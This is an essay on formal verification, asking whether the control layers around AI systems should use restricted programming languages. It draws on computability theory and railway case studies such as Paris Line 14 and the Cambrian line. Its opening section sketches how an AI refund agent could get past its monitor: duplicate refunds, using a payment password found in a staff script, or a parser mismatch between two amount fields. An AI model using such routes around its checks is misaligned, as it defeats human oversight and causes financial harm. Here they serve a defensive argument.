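# Should the control layers around powerful AI be written in deliberately non-Turing-complete languages?

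## What a restricted language can guarantee, and what it cannot

A restricted programming language is designed without some feature, most often loops that have no fixed limit, so that a computer can analyse the programs written in it. Engineers have relied on such languages in railway signalling and flight control for decades, and the Linux kernel accepts small programs written in one. Software companies have recently begun to use them for the controls around AI systems.

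An AI system of this kind combines a learned model, such as a neural network or a large language model, with a control layer. The model's behaviour comes from training on data rather than from code written line by line. The control layer is the conventional software that feeds the model its inputs, checks its outputs and carries out its actions. Because this layer is ordinary code, it is sometimes possible to prove things about it. Whether it is worth writing that code in a deliberately limited language depends on what the proofs would cover and what they would require.

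Suppose a shop lets an AI agent issue refunds. A customer writes that a kettle arrived broken. A wrapper collects the message and the order record and passes them to a language model, which outputs a request to refund 60 euros on order 4417. A monitor checks the request against the shop's rules, for instance that no refund may exceed what the customer paid. If the request passes, actuation code calls the payment provider, which refunds the money.

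The shop might want three different guarantees, which people easily confuse. A termination guarantee means that the monitor always finishes. Without it, a strange request can make the monitor hang. Refunds then stop for everybody or, if somebody has set the payment code to go ahead after a time-out, the money goes out unchecked. A conformance guarantee means that the monitor matches its specification, the precise statement of what it must do. A safety guarantee means that the harm itself does not occur, which in this case means that the shop does not lose money on refunds it should never have paid.

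A monitor that conforms to its specification can still be far from safe. Suppose the specification requires that no refund exceed the price of the order, and someone proves that the monitor enforces this on every possible request. The agent can still refund the same kettle twice, because the specification doesn't limit the total. It can also refund a kettle that was never broken. Or it might find the payment provider's password in a staff script and call the provider directly. The proof about the monitor would still hold, but it wouldn't prevent the payment. Preventing this bypass requires what security engineers call complete mediation, which means that every action must pass through the check.

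A restricted language can guarantee that programs terminate. It can also make conformance easy to check, but only with the right restriction, and finding that restriction is most of the difficulty. It can contribute to safety only through a correct specification and a check that cannot be bypassed.

### Why no tool can check every program

A language is Turing-complete if it can express any computation, given unlimited memory and time. Python, C and JavaScript all qualify, as do many things that people don't usually think of as programming languages. The web catalogue *Surprisingly Turing-Complete* includes the SVG image format and PowerPoint animations, although the animations need a user to keep clicking. It omits configuration formats because they turn out to be Turing-complete so often that it is no longer surprising. Any feature that substitutes one piece of text for another may be enough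 to make a language Turing-complete, so keeping a language restricted takes continued effort.

Nobody can predict in general what programs in a Turing-complete language will do. Alan Turing's work of 1936 and 1937 established, in substance, that no algorithm can determine for every program and every input whether the program will eventually halt. Suppose there were such an algorithm, halts(p, x), which always answers correctly whether program p stops on input x. Then anyone could write a second program, g, which takes the text of a program p and calls halts(p, p), then loops forever if the answer is yes and stops if the answer is no. If g is run on its own text and halts(g, g) returns yes, g loops forever; if it returns no, g stops. The answer is wrong in both cases, so no such algorithm exists. Logicians call a question decidable if some algorithm answers it correctly, in finite time, for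 every case, so the halting problem is undecidable.

More practical questions than halting are also undecidable. Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951 that every property of a program's behaviour is undecidable if some programs have it and others lack it. The refund monitor can illustrate the proof. Suppose a tool could determine whether any given monitor ever approves a refund above the price. For any program a and input i, we can write a monitor that first runs a on i, discards the result, and then approves whatever request came in. This monitor approves excessive refunds if a halts on i, and approves nothing if a runs forever. The tool could therefore be used to determine whether a halts on i, which no algorithm can do in general.

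Rice's theorem, though, is about how programs behave, not how they are written. Any compiler can check whether a program contains a while-loop. Restricted languages use this kind of check to reject programs based on their text, which guarantees something about how the remaining programs behave. The theorem is also about all programs at once. As *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines* (2024) notes, it does not rule out a machine that can determine whether some particular program behaves in a given way.

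Any fully automatic tool that checks behavioural properties of programs in a Turing-complete language will, on some programs, miss a real violation, raise a false alarm, or never produce an answer. An analysis is sound if it never misses a violation of the property it checks, within its model, and complete if it never raises a false alarm. For these programs, no tool that always finishes can be both sound and complete.

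### The price of analysis, rung by rung

Between a yes-or-no rule and a general program lie several intermediate formalisms, and the cost of analysis climbs steeply long before decidability gives out.

Boolean formulas are at the bottom. They combine yes-or-no facts with "and", "or" and "not". A refund rule at this level might approve a request if the order exists, nobody has refunded it before, and either the amount is small or a manager has signed. To find out whether the rule could ever approve a small refund on a non-existent order, an analyser looks for a combination of facts that makes it do so. With n facts there are 2^n combinations, which is about a million for twenty facts and more than 10^30 for a hundred. Solvers avoid most of that search on the formulas people write in practice, but nobody has published a method that is fast on every formula. Whether such a method exists is the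 P versus NP problem, which asks if a computer can always quickly find any solution that it can quickly check. *AI and P vs NP problem* (The News International, 2026) still described it as unsolved in late November 2026, and *Rumors swirl that AI models have already cracked math secrets* (Basu and Sabin, 2026) reported only rumours on the same day.

Finite-state machines add memory. A refund, for example, is always in one of five states (requested, awaiting a manager, approved, paid or refused), and a fixed table lists which events move it from one state to another. To check whether a refund can be paid without being approved, an analyser starts at "requested", follows every transition that avoids "approved", and sees whether it reaches "paid". The work is proportional to the size of the table, but the number of joint states grows exponentially with the number of independent parts. Ten refunds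 in progress at once have 5^10 joint states, nearly ten million, and every further yes-or-no fact that the system remembers doubles that number.

Rules about amounts of money need arithmetic. In linear integer arithmetic, which logicians call Presburger arithmetic, a formula can add whole numbers, compare them, multiply them by fixed constants, and use "every" and "some" to refer to them. "For every price p and every refund r, if the rule approves r then r is at most p" is a sentence of this kind. Mojżesz Presburger gave a procedure in 1929 for deciding whether any such sentence is true, as *Subclasses of Presburger Arithmetic and the Weak EXP Hierarchy* (2014) recounts. Fischer and Rabin proved in 1974 that any such procedure needs at least doubly exponential time in the worst case, meaning 2 raised to a power that grows exponentially with the length of the sentence. *Bounds on the Automata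 Size for Presburger Arithmetic* cites that result alongside Oppen's proof that one standard procedure takes triply exponential time. The best known method of the same type was still triply exponential when *The complexity of Presburger arithmetic with power or powers* (2023) appeared.

In practice people drop "every" and "some" and keep the rest. According to the 2014 paper, most applications use this quantifier-free fragment because it takes much less computation. An SMT solver, a program that decides whether a logical formula over numbers, strings and similar data can be true, handles it routinely. Cedar, a language for rules about single actions by AI agents, relies on such solvers. A seemingly harmless feature request can remove the guarantee that a solver will reach an answer. "Refund at most 80 per cent of the price" is linear because 80 per cent is a constant, but "refund at most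 the quantity times the unit price" multiplies two unknowns, and arithmetic with both addition and multiplication is undecidable for whole numbers of unlimited size.

*The complexity of loop programs* (Meyer and Ritchie, 1967) defines a more powerful language that looks like programming. Its registers hold non-negative whole numbers of any size, and it has five kinds of instruction: copy one register into another, add one to a register, set a register to zero, LOOP X, and END. Everything between LOOP X and its END runs as many times as the number X held on entry, even if the loop changes X. Because that count is fixed before the loop starts, every program halts. The language can still express addition, multiplication, exponentiation and finding the xth prime. Its programs compute exactly the primitive recursive functions, which include nearly every function anyone meets outside the theory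 of computation.

Some questions about programs are undecidable even in a language where every program halts. One is whether two loop programs compute the same function. In *The Equivalence Problem of Simple Programs* (1970), Dennis Tsichritzis gave an algorithm that decides this for programs without nested loops, and proved that no such algorithm exists once loops may nest two deep. Hunt, Constable and Sahni showed in *On the Computational Complexity of Program Scheme Equivalence* (1980) that even the decidable case is NP-complete, which makes it as hard as deciding whether a Boolean formula can be satisfied. For general programs, Rice's theorem shows that no nontrivial question about a program's behaviour is decidable.

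### Why termination does not settle the rest

How can a language in which nothing ever hangs be so hard to analyse? Take any machine M, meaning any program in a general-purpose language together with its input. Now write a bounded-loop program that takes a number n:

```
found = 0
LOOP n
    if M has not halted, carry out its next step
    if M has halted, found = 1
END
output found
```

One step of M is a small, fixed update, which the language can express with an inner loop or two. The program always finishes, because it simulates at most n steps. If M halts after t steps, the output is 0 for every n below t and 1 for every n from t on. If M never halts, the output is 0 for every n. So an algorithm that could determine whether a bounded-loop program outputs 0 on all inputs could also determine whether M halts, which no algorithm can do for every M. Matos (2016), in *Primitive recursive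 functions versus partial recursive functions*, derives the undecidability of this question, and of equivalence, from the same construction. Meyer and Ritchie had already used a very similar construction in a different proof. Theirs has one outer loop that runs a set number of times and, inside it, a flag for each instruction that marks whether it runs next.

A refund monitor could approve any request up to the price of the order, and approve a larger request of n cents only if a Turing machine M halts within n steps. The monitor answers every request, because it runs M for at most n steps. It follows the rule "never refund more than the price" if and only if M never halts. No general method can decide whether a Turing machine halts, so no general method can check monitors in this language against that rule.

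No tool can give the right answer for every program in the language, because it would fail on this monitor. Nobody would write such a monitor, though, and ordinary ones may be quite easy to check.

Guaranteed termination makes some properties of a program's behavior decidable. Matos points out that Rice's theorem is false for primitive recursive functions, because you can find out whether an always-halting program outputs 0 on input 5 by running it on 5. Hoyrup (2015), in *A Rice-like theorem for primitive recursive functions*, worked out exactly which properties are decidable. From the text of an always-halting program, an algorithm can establish what the program outputs on a finite list of inputs. It can also establish certain facts about how simple the outputs are, roughly whether a program early in the list of all programs would reproduce them. Every decidable property reduces to combinations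 of those two. "For every request, the refund is at most the price" does not, so it is undecidable.

Requiring speed as well as termination doesn't help. Hoyrup's theorem covers the functions computable in polynomial time, the usual theoretical standard for "fast", and the construction above also works for them if M is simulated for as many steps as the input has digits.

*Surprisingly Turing-Complete* suggests that in a language short of Turing-completeness, it may be easy to prove that programs terminate, that they use bounded resources, or that two implementations are equivalent. That is fair for the least expressive of these languages, but no general method can prove equivalence once bounded loops are nested two deep. "Non-Turing-complete" is therefore the wrong criterion. A team that wants automatic conformance checks needs to know how expressive its rules are, and the absence of infinite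 loops tells it little about that.

### Finishing, eventually

Even the termination guarantee is weaker than it looks. Here is a complete program in Meyer and Ritchie's language, a slight variant of one in Wikipedia's *LOOP (programming language)*:

```
Y = 0
Y = Y + 1
LOOP X
    LOOP Y
        Y = Y + 1
    END
END
```

The inner loop adds one to Y as many times as the value of Y on entry, so it doubles Y. The outer loop does this X times, leaving 2^X in Y. With X at 10, the program performs about a thousand additions. It always halts, but on a machine that performs a billion additions a second, it takes about 37 years with X at 60 and about 40 trillion years with X at 100. A third loop around these two could, on each pass, copy Y into X, reset Y to 1 and run the doubling again. Starting from Y = 1, successive passes would leave 2, 4, 16 and 65,536 in Y, and then a number with 19,729 digits.

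Meyer and Ritchie made this exact. They defined a sequence of bounds, each of which iterates the one before. f₁(x) is 2x, f₂(x) is 2^x, f₃(x) is a tower of x twos, each the exponent of the one below, and in general fₙ₊₁(x) is fₙ applied x times, starting from 1. A program of k instructions with loops nested n deep runs for no longer than fₙ applied k times to its largest input. Such bounds attracted theorists to the language. The draft of Ritchie's thesis, *Program Structure and Computational Complexity*, set out to show that a suitable restriction on the language ties the complexity of a program to the complexity of what it computes, so that one can read a bound on the running time from the program's text. The bound is seldom useful in practice. Meyer and Ritchie remark that a program that really needs f₇ "might just as well contain an infinite loop", because it would outlast the galaxy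 for inputs above two.

An analyser also cannot always tell whether a deeply nested program runs quickly. If T is zero, for example, a loop that begins with LOOP T never runs, so the program finishes in one step however complex the code inside the loop is. A tool can recognise this case and many like it, but Meyer and Ritchie proved that, among programs with three or more levels of nesting, no algorithm can identify every one that runs faster than its loops suggest.

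A refund monitor must finish by a deadline. The usual way to ensure this is a stricter restriction, under which every loop has a fixed limit in the program text that no input can raise. If three nested loops each have a limit of ten, the innermost block runs at most a thousand times, and an engineer can calculate this before deploying the code.

### Proofs about ordinary programs on finite machines

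There are two reasons not to rely too heavily on the undecidability results as an argument for restricted languages, even those on the lower rungs. Meyer and Ritchie gave the first in their opening paragraph, where they noted that algorithms may still solve a formally undecidable problem in the cases people care about. People may also be able to solve such cases themselves.

The best-known demonstration is seL4, an operating-system microkernel, the small core that controls memory and keeps programs apart from one another. Its developers wrote it largely in C, a Turing-complete language with few safeguards. *seL4*, a paper in *Communications of the ACM*, reports that the kernel comprises 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembler, and that its developers proved that the C code conforms to an abstract specification of the kernel's behaviour. They checked the whole proof with a proof assistant,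 a program that checks each logical step. The proof also rules out buffer overflows, null-pointer errors and other familiar classes of bug. Rice's theorem does not prevent such a proof, because it excludes only a single method that works for all programs, and the seL4 team needed a proof about one particular program.

The seL4 project is also unusually frank about what its proof assumes. *What the Proofs Assume* lists about 1,200 lines of start-up code, the hand-written assembly code, the hardware, and devices that write to memory without going through the processor. The proof that secrets do not leak does not cover leaks through timing. On some processors, an automatic tool checks the compiled binary against the C code, so the compiler need not be trusted. Everything that must be correct for a guarantee to hold is called the trusted computing base. A restricted language has one too, which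 includes its compiler, its analyser, and the machine that runs the result. The seL4 project also warns that users may expect things of the kernel that the proved properties do not capture, so even a proof this strong can have the same gap as the example of the twice-refunded kettle.

The second reason is that real computers are finite, while Turing's argument applies only to machines with unlimited memory. A machine with a fixed number of bits has a fixed number of possible states, so a program that never halts must eventually return to an earlier state and then repeat itself forever. In principle, one can therefore decide whether any program on an actual computer halts by running it until it either stops or returns to an earlier state. The undecidable questions about refunds also become decidable in principle once amounts have a maximum size.

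The principle is of little use. A machine with a million bits of memory has 2^1,000,000 states, a number with about 300,000 digits. Testing every possible value of a single 64-bit amount, at a billion a second, would take 585 years. For real systems, then, decidability is a proxy for what matters, which is whether an analysis is feasible with the time and computing power available.

On that reading, the case for a restricted language is mostly that it makes verification less work for people. The seL4 proof needed specialists, and a change to the kernel can require them to revise it. A solver can usually recheck a refund rule written in quantifier-free linear arithmetic after each edit without anyone's help. That advantage is now shrinking as AI reduces the work people must do to prove things about general-purpose code.

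### Restricting what a program accepts

The restrictions discussed so far apply to the language of the control layer's own code, but designers can also restrict the language of its inputs. Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues (2011) set out this approach, called language-theoretic security, for network software in *The Halting Problems of Network Stack Insecurity*. The set of inputs that a program is meant to accept is a language in the mathematical sense, and the parser, which is the code that reads input, is a machine for recognising it. An attack is then a crafted input that makes the receiving system carry out a computation its designers never intended. The paper argues that computational power is therefore a privilege like any other, and that designers should give the sender of an input as little of it as the job allows.

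Sassaman and colleagues measure a language's power by the Chomsky hierarchy. A finite-state machine can recognise the simplest languages, the regular ones. Context-free languages allow nested structures, so recognising them also takes a stack. Languages above those need far more, up to a full Turing machine. The paper advises designers to stay at or below the unambiguous context-free level. It applies this to SQL, the database query language, where attackers can insert commands through web forms. Programmers often try to filter out bad inputs with regular expressions, which are too weak for this. It is better to define the small subset of SQL that the application needs and generate a parser for it. A refund monitor can go further and accept only an order number and an amount from the model.

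Their second principle is even more relevant to monitors. When two components read the same message, security depends on both of them interpreting it the same way. One of their examples is the certificate a website uses to prove its identity. A certificate could list several names, such as an attacker's first and a bank's second. One widely used library read only the first name, while Internet Explorer also accepted the certificate as the bank's. Intrusion detectors had the same weakness, because attackers could send traffic that the detector reassembled into one conversation and its target into another. Suppose a refund request carries two "amount" fields, 60 and 6,000. If the monitor reads the first and the payment code reads the second, even a flawless monitor will approve 60 euros while the shop pays out 6,000. Whether two parsers accept the same language is decidable for regular and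 deterministic context-free languages and undecidable beyond them, so Tsichritzis's barrier applies here too. Even where the question is decidable, the check only covers which messages the parsers accept. The designers must still specify which of two amounts counts or, better, forbid the second.

A language can express any computation and still be very easy to recognise. Taylor Hornby made this point on the field's mailing list, objecting that the field's literature confuses what a language can compute with how hard it is to recognise. Sassaman and colleagues, for example, write that once SQL became Turing-complete, validating it became hopeless, because recognising such a language is undecidable. Hornby's counterexample is a minimal Turing-complete programming language with eight symbols, whose grammar is context-free and fits on four lines. One can even write programs in the set of all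 strings, which is a regular language.

Hornby is right on the theory. It is usually easy to check whether a text is a well-formed program, but what the program will do when it runs is undecidable. The advice survives if "valid" means "harmless to execute", because that is a property of behaviour and Rice's theorem applies to it. Sassaman and colleagues partly draw this distinction when they separate an input's grammar from its effect on the state of the receiving system. For the shop, the distinction determines what the model may send. An order number and an amount contain nothing to execute, but if the model sent a script to compute the refund, the monitor would have to work out what the script does, however simple its grammar.

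Hornby also complains that a correct parser does nothing about bugs in the code behind it. The paper Hornby criticizes had already conceded that a provably correct parser reduces what an attacker can reach but doesn't make the system unexploitable. For example, a correct parser would accept a second request to refund order 4417, because it is as well-formed as the first.

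## Railway signalling: Paris Métro Line 14 and interlocking logic

An interlocking sits between a signaller and the track, much as the refund monitor sits between an agent and the shop's money. The signaller asks for a route through a junction, and the interlocking sets it only if no other train can be in the way. Engineers built the first interlockings from levers and locking bars, and later ones from relays, which are electrical switches that are either open or closed. Many are now computers that do much the same thing. *Applying a Formal Method in Industry* (Lecomte, Deharbe et al., 2020) describes the software as computing Boolean equations over the track state reported by sensors, so that two trains never share a section.

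The equations can be Boolean because every fact they use is a yes or a no. A section of track is occupied or clear, a set of points lies one way or the other, and a route is set or not. A station has a fixed number of these facts, so it has a finite number of states. The logic needs no loops, so railway engineers lost nothing by using a language with so little expressive power.

### Two routes and one piece of track

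Suppose routes A and B both cross a track section T. A computer recalculates the state of both routes several times a second from seven yes-or-no values: whether each route is set, whether a signaller is asking for it, whether the signaller is releasing it, and whether a train occupies T. A first attempt at the equations might be:

```
A_new = (A and not release_A) or (ask_A and not B and not T)
B_new = (B and not release_B) or (ask_B and not A and not T)
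```

A route that is set stays set until somebody releases it. A route becomes set only if somebody requests it, the other route is not set, and the section is clear. The safety rule is that routes A and B are never both set.

There are infinitely many possible histories of requests, so nobody can test them all, but an analyser can prove the rule by induction. It first checks that the rule holds at the start, when neither route is set. It then checks that no single cycle can break the rule, by combining every state that obeys it with every possible input and examining the state that follows. If both checks pass, the rule holds after any number of cycles.

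Seven yes-or-no values have 128 combinations, and the rule holds beforehand in 96 of them. Going through those 96 turns up a failure. If neither route is set, T is clear, and requests for both routes arrive in the same cycle, each equation uses the old value of the other route, and both routes become set. A tester who tries one request at a time would never see this. The repair is to calculate A first and use its new value for B:

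```
B_new = (B and not release_B) or (ask_B and not A_new and not T)
```

Suppose both routes were set after some cycle. B can become set only if A_new is false, so B must have been set before the cycle. A can become set only if B was unset, so A must also have been set before the cycle. This contradicts the assumption that the rule held before the cycle, so no cycle can break it.

A rule can also be true and still fail this check. Suppose each of two routes has a signal that turns green one cycle after the route is set, and the rule is that the two signals are never both green. The check has to consider a state in which both routes are set but neither signal is green yet. That state obeys the rule, but the next one breaks it. The system can never reach such a state, but the signal rule does not exclude it. An engineer can add the rule that the two routes are never both set and prove the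 two rules together. Alternatively, a tool can assume that the signal rule held for two cycles in a row and prove it for the third. This technique, called k-induction, works here. David Bonvoisin's *25 years of Formal Methods at RATP* describes a tool that combines k-induction with Boolean solvers. RATP, which operates the Paris metro, uses the tool to check its suppliers' software independently.

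None of this proves anything about the track itself. If rust on the rails stops a sensor from detecting a train, T is false while the train stands on the section, and the interlocking can route another train into that section without violating any equation.

### From a specification to Ada

Line 14, which opened in October 1998, was the first driverless metro line in Paris. *Météor* (Behm, Benoit and colleagues, 1999) explains that Matra Transport International developed its control system for RATP, with safety-critical software on the trains, along the track and in a central unit. Software of this kind needs more than Boolean logic, because it has to work out where a train is and whether it can brake in time. According to Lecomte and colleagues, that involves whole-number arithmetic, tables that describe the track, and graph algorithms. No tool can settle every question about such programs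 automatically. Matra's engineers used the B method, in which people develop a program and its proof together. In *Formal Methods*, Jean-Raymond Abrial, who invented the method, compares its models to an engineer's blueprints, which people can reason about before they build anything.

To illustrate the steps with an invented example, suppose the software must calculate a train's maximum permitted speed, given the speed restrictions on the track ahead.

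The engineers first write an abstract specification in the language of logic and set theory. For example, it might require only that the resulting speed not exceed the line speed or any restriction in force. It does not define how to find such a speed, and it allows several answers, including zero. Many safety specifications can be met by a train that never moves. Lecomte (2007) notes in *Formal Methods in Safety-Critical Railway Systems* that specifications in B contain no loops or sequences of instructions.

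The next step is refinement, in which the engineers replace abstract descriptions with more concrete ones. Here they might replace the set of restrictions with a numbered table, and "some speed no higher than" with "the lowest of these speeds". They must prove that the old version allowed every answer the new version can give. A large program may need several such steps.

At the end comes the implementation, in a subset of the language called B0, which has only the data types and instructions that a computer can execute directly. In slightly simplified notation:

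```
limit := line_speed
i := 0
WHILE i < n DO
    i := i + 1
    IF table(i) < limit THEN limit := table(i) END
INVARIANT  0 <= i <= n, and limit is no higher than
           line_speed or any of the first i entries
VARIANT    n - i
END
```

A tool called Atelier B generates the proof obligations, the statements that somebody must prove before the code counts as correct. For this loop, they include that the invariant is true on entry, that each pass keeps it true, that it implies the specification once i reaches n, that no number overflows, and that the program never reads outside the table. An automatic prover tries each one, and engineers guide it through the rest. Once all are proved, a translator converts the B0 code into Ada, a general-purpose programming language. Abrial reports that the engineers on Line 14 did not modify the Ada afterwards.

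### A termination proof for every loop

B's grammar allows a WHILE loop whose condition is always true, whereas Meyer and Ritchie's loop language cannot express a program that runs forever. But every loop in B must come with a variant, a whole number that the engineer has to prove is never negative and gets smaller with each pass. In the example, the variant starts at n and falls by one each time. An endless loop has no such variant, so the engineer can never prove all its proof obligations, and the development cannot be completed. B's structure rules out recursion, because a component can call only the components it imports, and imports may not form a circle.

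So the termination guarantee on Line 14 came from proofs about individual loops. This is more flexible than a fixed limit on every loop, because the engineer can use any quantity that keeps shrinking. A person may have to find that quantity, but it is obvious for most loops in control software.

The control program as a whole must never stop. Abrial describes the safety-critical part of each unit as a single uninterruptible task that repeats every 350 milliseconds. The termination proofs show that the work in each cycle eventually finishes. Engineers have to establish separately that it finishes within 350 milliseconds, because that depends on the processor.

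B0's other restrictions probably matter more for the proofs. It has no pointers, and programs cannot allocate more memory while running. The generated program has no threads (parts that run at the same time and can interfere with each other). An engineer proving something about one line therefore doesn't have to consider what else might have changed the data.

### Counting the lines and the proofs

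Abrial gives figures for Line 14 and for a later B project, the driverless shuttle at Roissy airport outside Paris:

| | Line 14 | Roissy shuttle |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of B | 115,000 | 183,000 |
| Lines of Ada generated | 86,000 | 158,000 |
| Proof obligations | 27,800 | 43,610 |
| Share proved interactively | 8.1% | 3.3% |
| Interactive proof effort, in person-months | 7.1 | 4.6 |

On Line 14, people had to guide the proofs of about 2,250 obligations. Abrial calculated the 7.1 person-months by assuming that one person completes 15 interactive proofs a day, 21 days a month, not from records of hours worked. Even if the true figure was twice as high, it would be modest for a system of this size.

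In *Formal methods scalability, some real-world figures*, Mentré (2014) breaks down the effort on a larger B project, the control system for the Canarsie line of the New York subway. Four people spent seven months writing the requirements in formal language. Refinement, proof and functional testing then each took three people three months. Proof therefore took 9 of the 55 person-months, while writing the requirements took 28.

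The share of proofs that need a person has not fallen steadily over time, either. In a more recent train-protection project that Lecomte and colleagues describe, 17% of 23,000 obligations needed interactive proof. The engineers also added 3,000 mathematical rules to help the prover, and had to justify 15% of those rules by hand.

Sources disagree about the amount of code on Line 14. Abrial gives 86,000 lines for the Ada generated from B, which covers the safety-critical functions and makes up about a third of the whole program. Lecomte gives the same number, but Bonvoisin's slides give 150,000 lines of Ada generated from B, with no explanation of the count. That cannot be the whole program, which would be roughly 260,000 lines if the B part is a third of it. The most likely explanation is a mix-up with the Roissy shuttle, for which Lecomte gives 150,000 lines and Abrial 158,000. The 86,000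 figure is better supported for Line 14.

### Who vouches for the record

Lecomte wrote in 2007 that functional validation, integration, on-site testing and nine years of service had revealed no bugs in Line 14's safety-critical software since engineers completed the proofs, and that the software was still at version 1.0. Lecomte and colleagues wrote in 2020 that no bug had appeared since the line opened. ClearSy's *Extension of Line 14 of the Paris Metro* (2024) claims more than 25 years of reliability. All three accounts come from ClearSy, which develops and distributes Atelier B.

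There is less evidence from people with a smaller commercial interest. Abrial, who is not neutral because the method is his own, reports that Matra skipped unit tests, which exercise small pieces of code separately, and that the tests of the whole program all succeeded. CLEARSY quotes an RATP manager who in April 1998, before the line opened, called the software "almost perfect the first time", which is high praise but doesn't mean it had no bugs. Bonvoisin, who speaks for the operator, gives no bug count. His slides show that RATP accepted further B-developed train control systems in 2011 and 2013, so it was presumably satisfied.

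The central claim is probably true, because a dangerous software fault on a driverless line with 350,000 passengers a day would be hard to hide for decades, though a harmless one could be hidden. "No bugs" means no known departures from the specification in the part of the software developed with B, so it is not evidence about the other two thirds.

The record also does not show how many bugs Matra would have had without B. The closest comparison is SACEM, an earlier train-protection system on a suburban line in the Paris region. Its developers wrote more than 60,000 lines in Modula-2, a general-purpose language, and RATP then grew worried about the safety of the code. Engineers working with Abrial modelled the existing code in a formal notation called Z. According to Bonvoisin, they found and corrected about 20 unsafe scenarios before the system entered service in 1989. That experience led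 RATP to support the development of B, but the modelling had found serious faults in code that was not written in a restricted language.

When RATP began replacing old relay interlockings in 2001, it tried modelling the principles of interlocking in B and judged the approach not fully adequate. B was too different from what signalling engineers knew, and none of the suppliers built interlockings with it. Bonvoisin reports that RATP instead chose a system that describes interlockings as Petri nets, which are diagrams of states and transitions, and used a model checker to prove their safety properties. This makes sense for a finite system of yes-or-no facts, because a tool can do nearly all of the proof. RATP has since turned to a newly designed safety relay, partly because commercial computers last less than 20 years, and is adapting its proof tool to read the wiring diagrams.

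### The prover, the compiler and the processor

The guarantee on Line 14 also depends on Atelier B, which its makers did not develop formally. In *FACS FACTS* (2026), the newsletter of the British Computer Society's formal methods group, Thierry Lecomte of ClearSy describes how they checked it. Atelier B's prover relies on more than 2,700 mathematical rules, and one false rule could let it "prove" something untrue. In 1995 the makers used a separate tool to try to verify 1,535 of the rules and found 59 to be false. They corrected 55 and removed the other four. For rules the tool could not handle, somebody wrote a proof by hand, and a panel of about ten people from five companies reviewed it.

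Even so, the developers have corrected a few tens of rules since 1998. They often found the error because Atelier B had accepted an incorrect model. Most of these rules were nearly right but lacked a condition limiting when they apply. Lecomte states in *FACS FACTS* that none of the errors led to a wrong proof of a safety-related obligation. This claim again comes from the toolmaker, though it accompanies an unusually candid list of faults.

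Even after the proofs are complete, the translator, the Ada compiler or the processor may introduce an error. Behm and colleagues explain that Matra combined B with the Vital Coded Processor. This device stores every number in a redundant form that reveals most errors. For example, suppose the computer multiplies each value by 97 and adds a signature unique to the variable. With a signature of 12, a speed of 40 becomes 97 × 40 + 12 = 3,892. With a signature of 30, a margin of 5 becomes 97 × 5 + 30 = 515. Dividing their sum, 4,407, by 97 leaves a remainder of 42, which is the sum of the two signatures.

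If a fault flips a single bit in the result, it changes the number by a power of two, which is never a multiple of 97, so the remainder is wrong. If the processor adds the speed to itself instead of to the margin, the remainder is 24. A real coded processor uses a much larger number than 97, so a random error is very unlikely to go unnoticed, and it adds a time stamp so that old data can be detected. A separate circuit compares the signatures with values calculated in advance and cuts off the output if they differ, which puts the train into a safe state. Because the expected signatures come from the source code, the comparison can also catch some compiler errors.

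The B method guards against mistakes in the program, while the coded processor guards against the machine failing to execute it correctly. Neither can detect a wrong specification or wrong input data.

### What the European standard asks of a language

The railway industry does not require languages like B, despite Line 14's well-known success. For many years the European standard for railway software was EN 50128, which grades software by safety integrity level (SIL), from 1 to 4. SIL 4 is for functions where a dangerous failure must occur less than about once in a billion hours. Bonvoisin notes that the standard "highly recommended" formal methods at SIL 3 and SIL 4, but a project could still choose other techniques if it justified them. The 2011 edition listed Ada and C, both Turing-complete, among its suitable languages, and relied on coding rules to discourage risky features such as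 dynamic memory and unlimited recursion.

CENELEC's *Railway Applications* (2023), or EN 50716, replaced EN 50128 and still has tables of coding standards and suitable programming languages. The Austrian edition, OVE's *Bahnanwendungen* (2024), allowed EN 50128 to remain in use until 30 October 2026. Verifysoft's *EN 50716 Railway Applications*, a page from a testing-tool vendor, reports that the new standard highly recommends static analysis, which examines code without running it, at all four safety integrity levels. The standard therefore restricts how engineers use a language and check the result, but it does not require a language that guarantees programs will terminate.

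The new standard also covers machine learning. A draft amendment, EVS's *EN 50716:2023/prA1:2026* (2026), would add guidance on using it in areas that are not safety-critical. It would leave the technical requirements unchanged, because there is not yet an accepted way to verify machine learning on railways.

### The missing speed restrictions on the Cambrian line

On 20 October 2017, a passenger train on the Cambrian Coast line in Wales went through a 30 km/h speed restriction at about 80 km/h. The restriction was meant to give people at a level crossing enough time to see a train coming. Nobody was hurt. The UK's Rail Accident Investigation Branch traced the cause in *Loss of safety critical signalling data on the Cambrian Coast line* (2019).

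The line has no trackside signals. A computer called the radio block centre sends each train its permission to proceed and its maximum speed, and equipment on board enforces both. Signallers entered temporary speed restrictions through a separate system called GEST, which passed them to the radio block centre. Seven restrictions were in force that day, all for level crossings.

Just after 23:00 the previous evening, the radio block centre restarted itself, as it was designed to do for safety when train permissions conflicted. This happened 10 to 12 times a year. Each restart erased temporary speed restrictions from the computer's memory but not permanent limits, so GEST had to send the temporary ones again.

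One thread of GEST's server software exchanged data with the signallers' terminal, another with the radio block centre, and the "Operation" thread carried information between them. The Operation thread had stopped, probably after reading a corrupted database record. Automatic checks covered the two outside connections, which still worked, but nothing checked the Operation thread.

The radio block centre therefore received no restrictions and behaved as if there were none. The terminal received no updates either, so it kept displaying the restrictions from before the restart, with green flags marking them as in force. The software should also have disabled the button for resuming service until the two systems agreed, but the same fault left it enabled. The signallers compared the screen with their printed list, as the procedure required, and the two matched. The next morning, three trains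 ran over the line before the driver of a fourth reported a problem.

RAIB could not confirm the database corruption because staff had deleted the relevant data while trying to get trains running again. But in laboratory tests, stopping the Operation thread reproduced the failure, and none of the other faults the engineers tried did.

A termination guarantee would have been useless here, because the problem was that the Operation thread terminated. GEST needed a guarantee that the restrictions would reach the radio block centre after every restart.

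The software also violated a written safety requirement that the data on the signallers' screen must always be consistent with the data from the radio block centre. RAIB found that the test meant to cover this requirement did not check it, and that the supplier, Ansaldo STS, had no documented analysis of what would happen if a thread failed. A proof might have exposed the fault, but only if its model included a thread that stops while the others keep running.

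The more fundamental fault was an omission from the specification. GEST was built only to SIL 2, while the speed restrictions needed SIL 4. The designers meant the signallers' visual check to make up the difference, but that could work only if the screen got its data by a different path from the one that uploaded the restrictions, and nobody wrote this requirement down. Engineers in France prepared the software requirements, engineers in Spain built the software, and the display and the upload ended up depending on the same thread. RAIB concluded that the Spanish team probably didn't know that the paths had to be separate.

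A proof of the speed-limit loop's code would have helped little on its own. Given an empty table, the loop returns the full line speed of 80 km/h. This is correct, because that speed exceeds no restriction in the table. The proof would therefore still hold while the train approached the crossing too fast. The railway mainly lacked a safety guarantee for the whole system, covering how the table gets filled and what the railway does when nobody can be sure that the table is complete.

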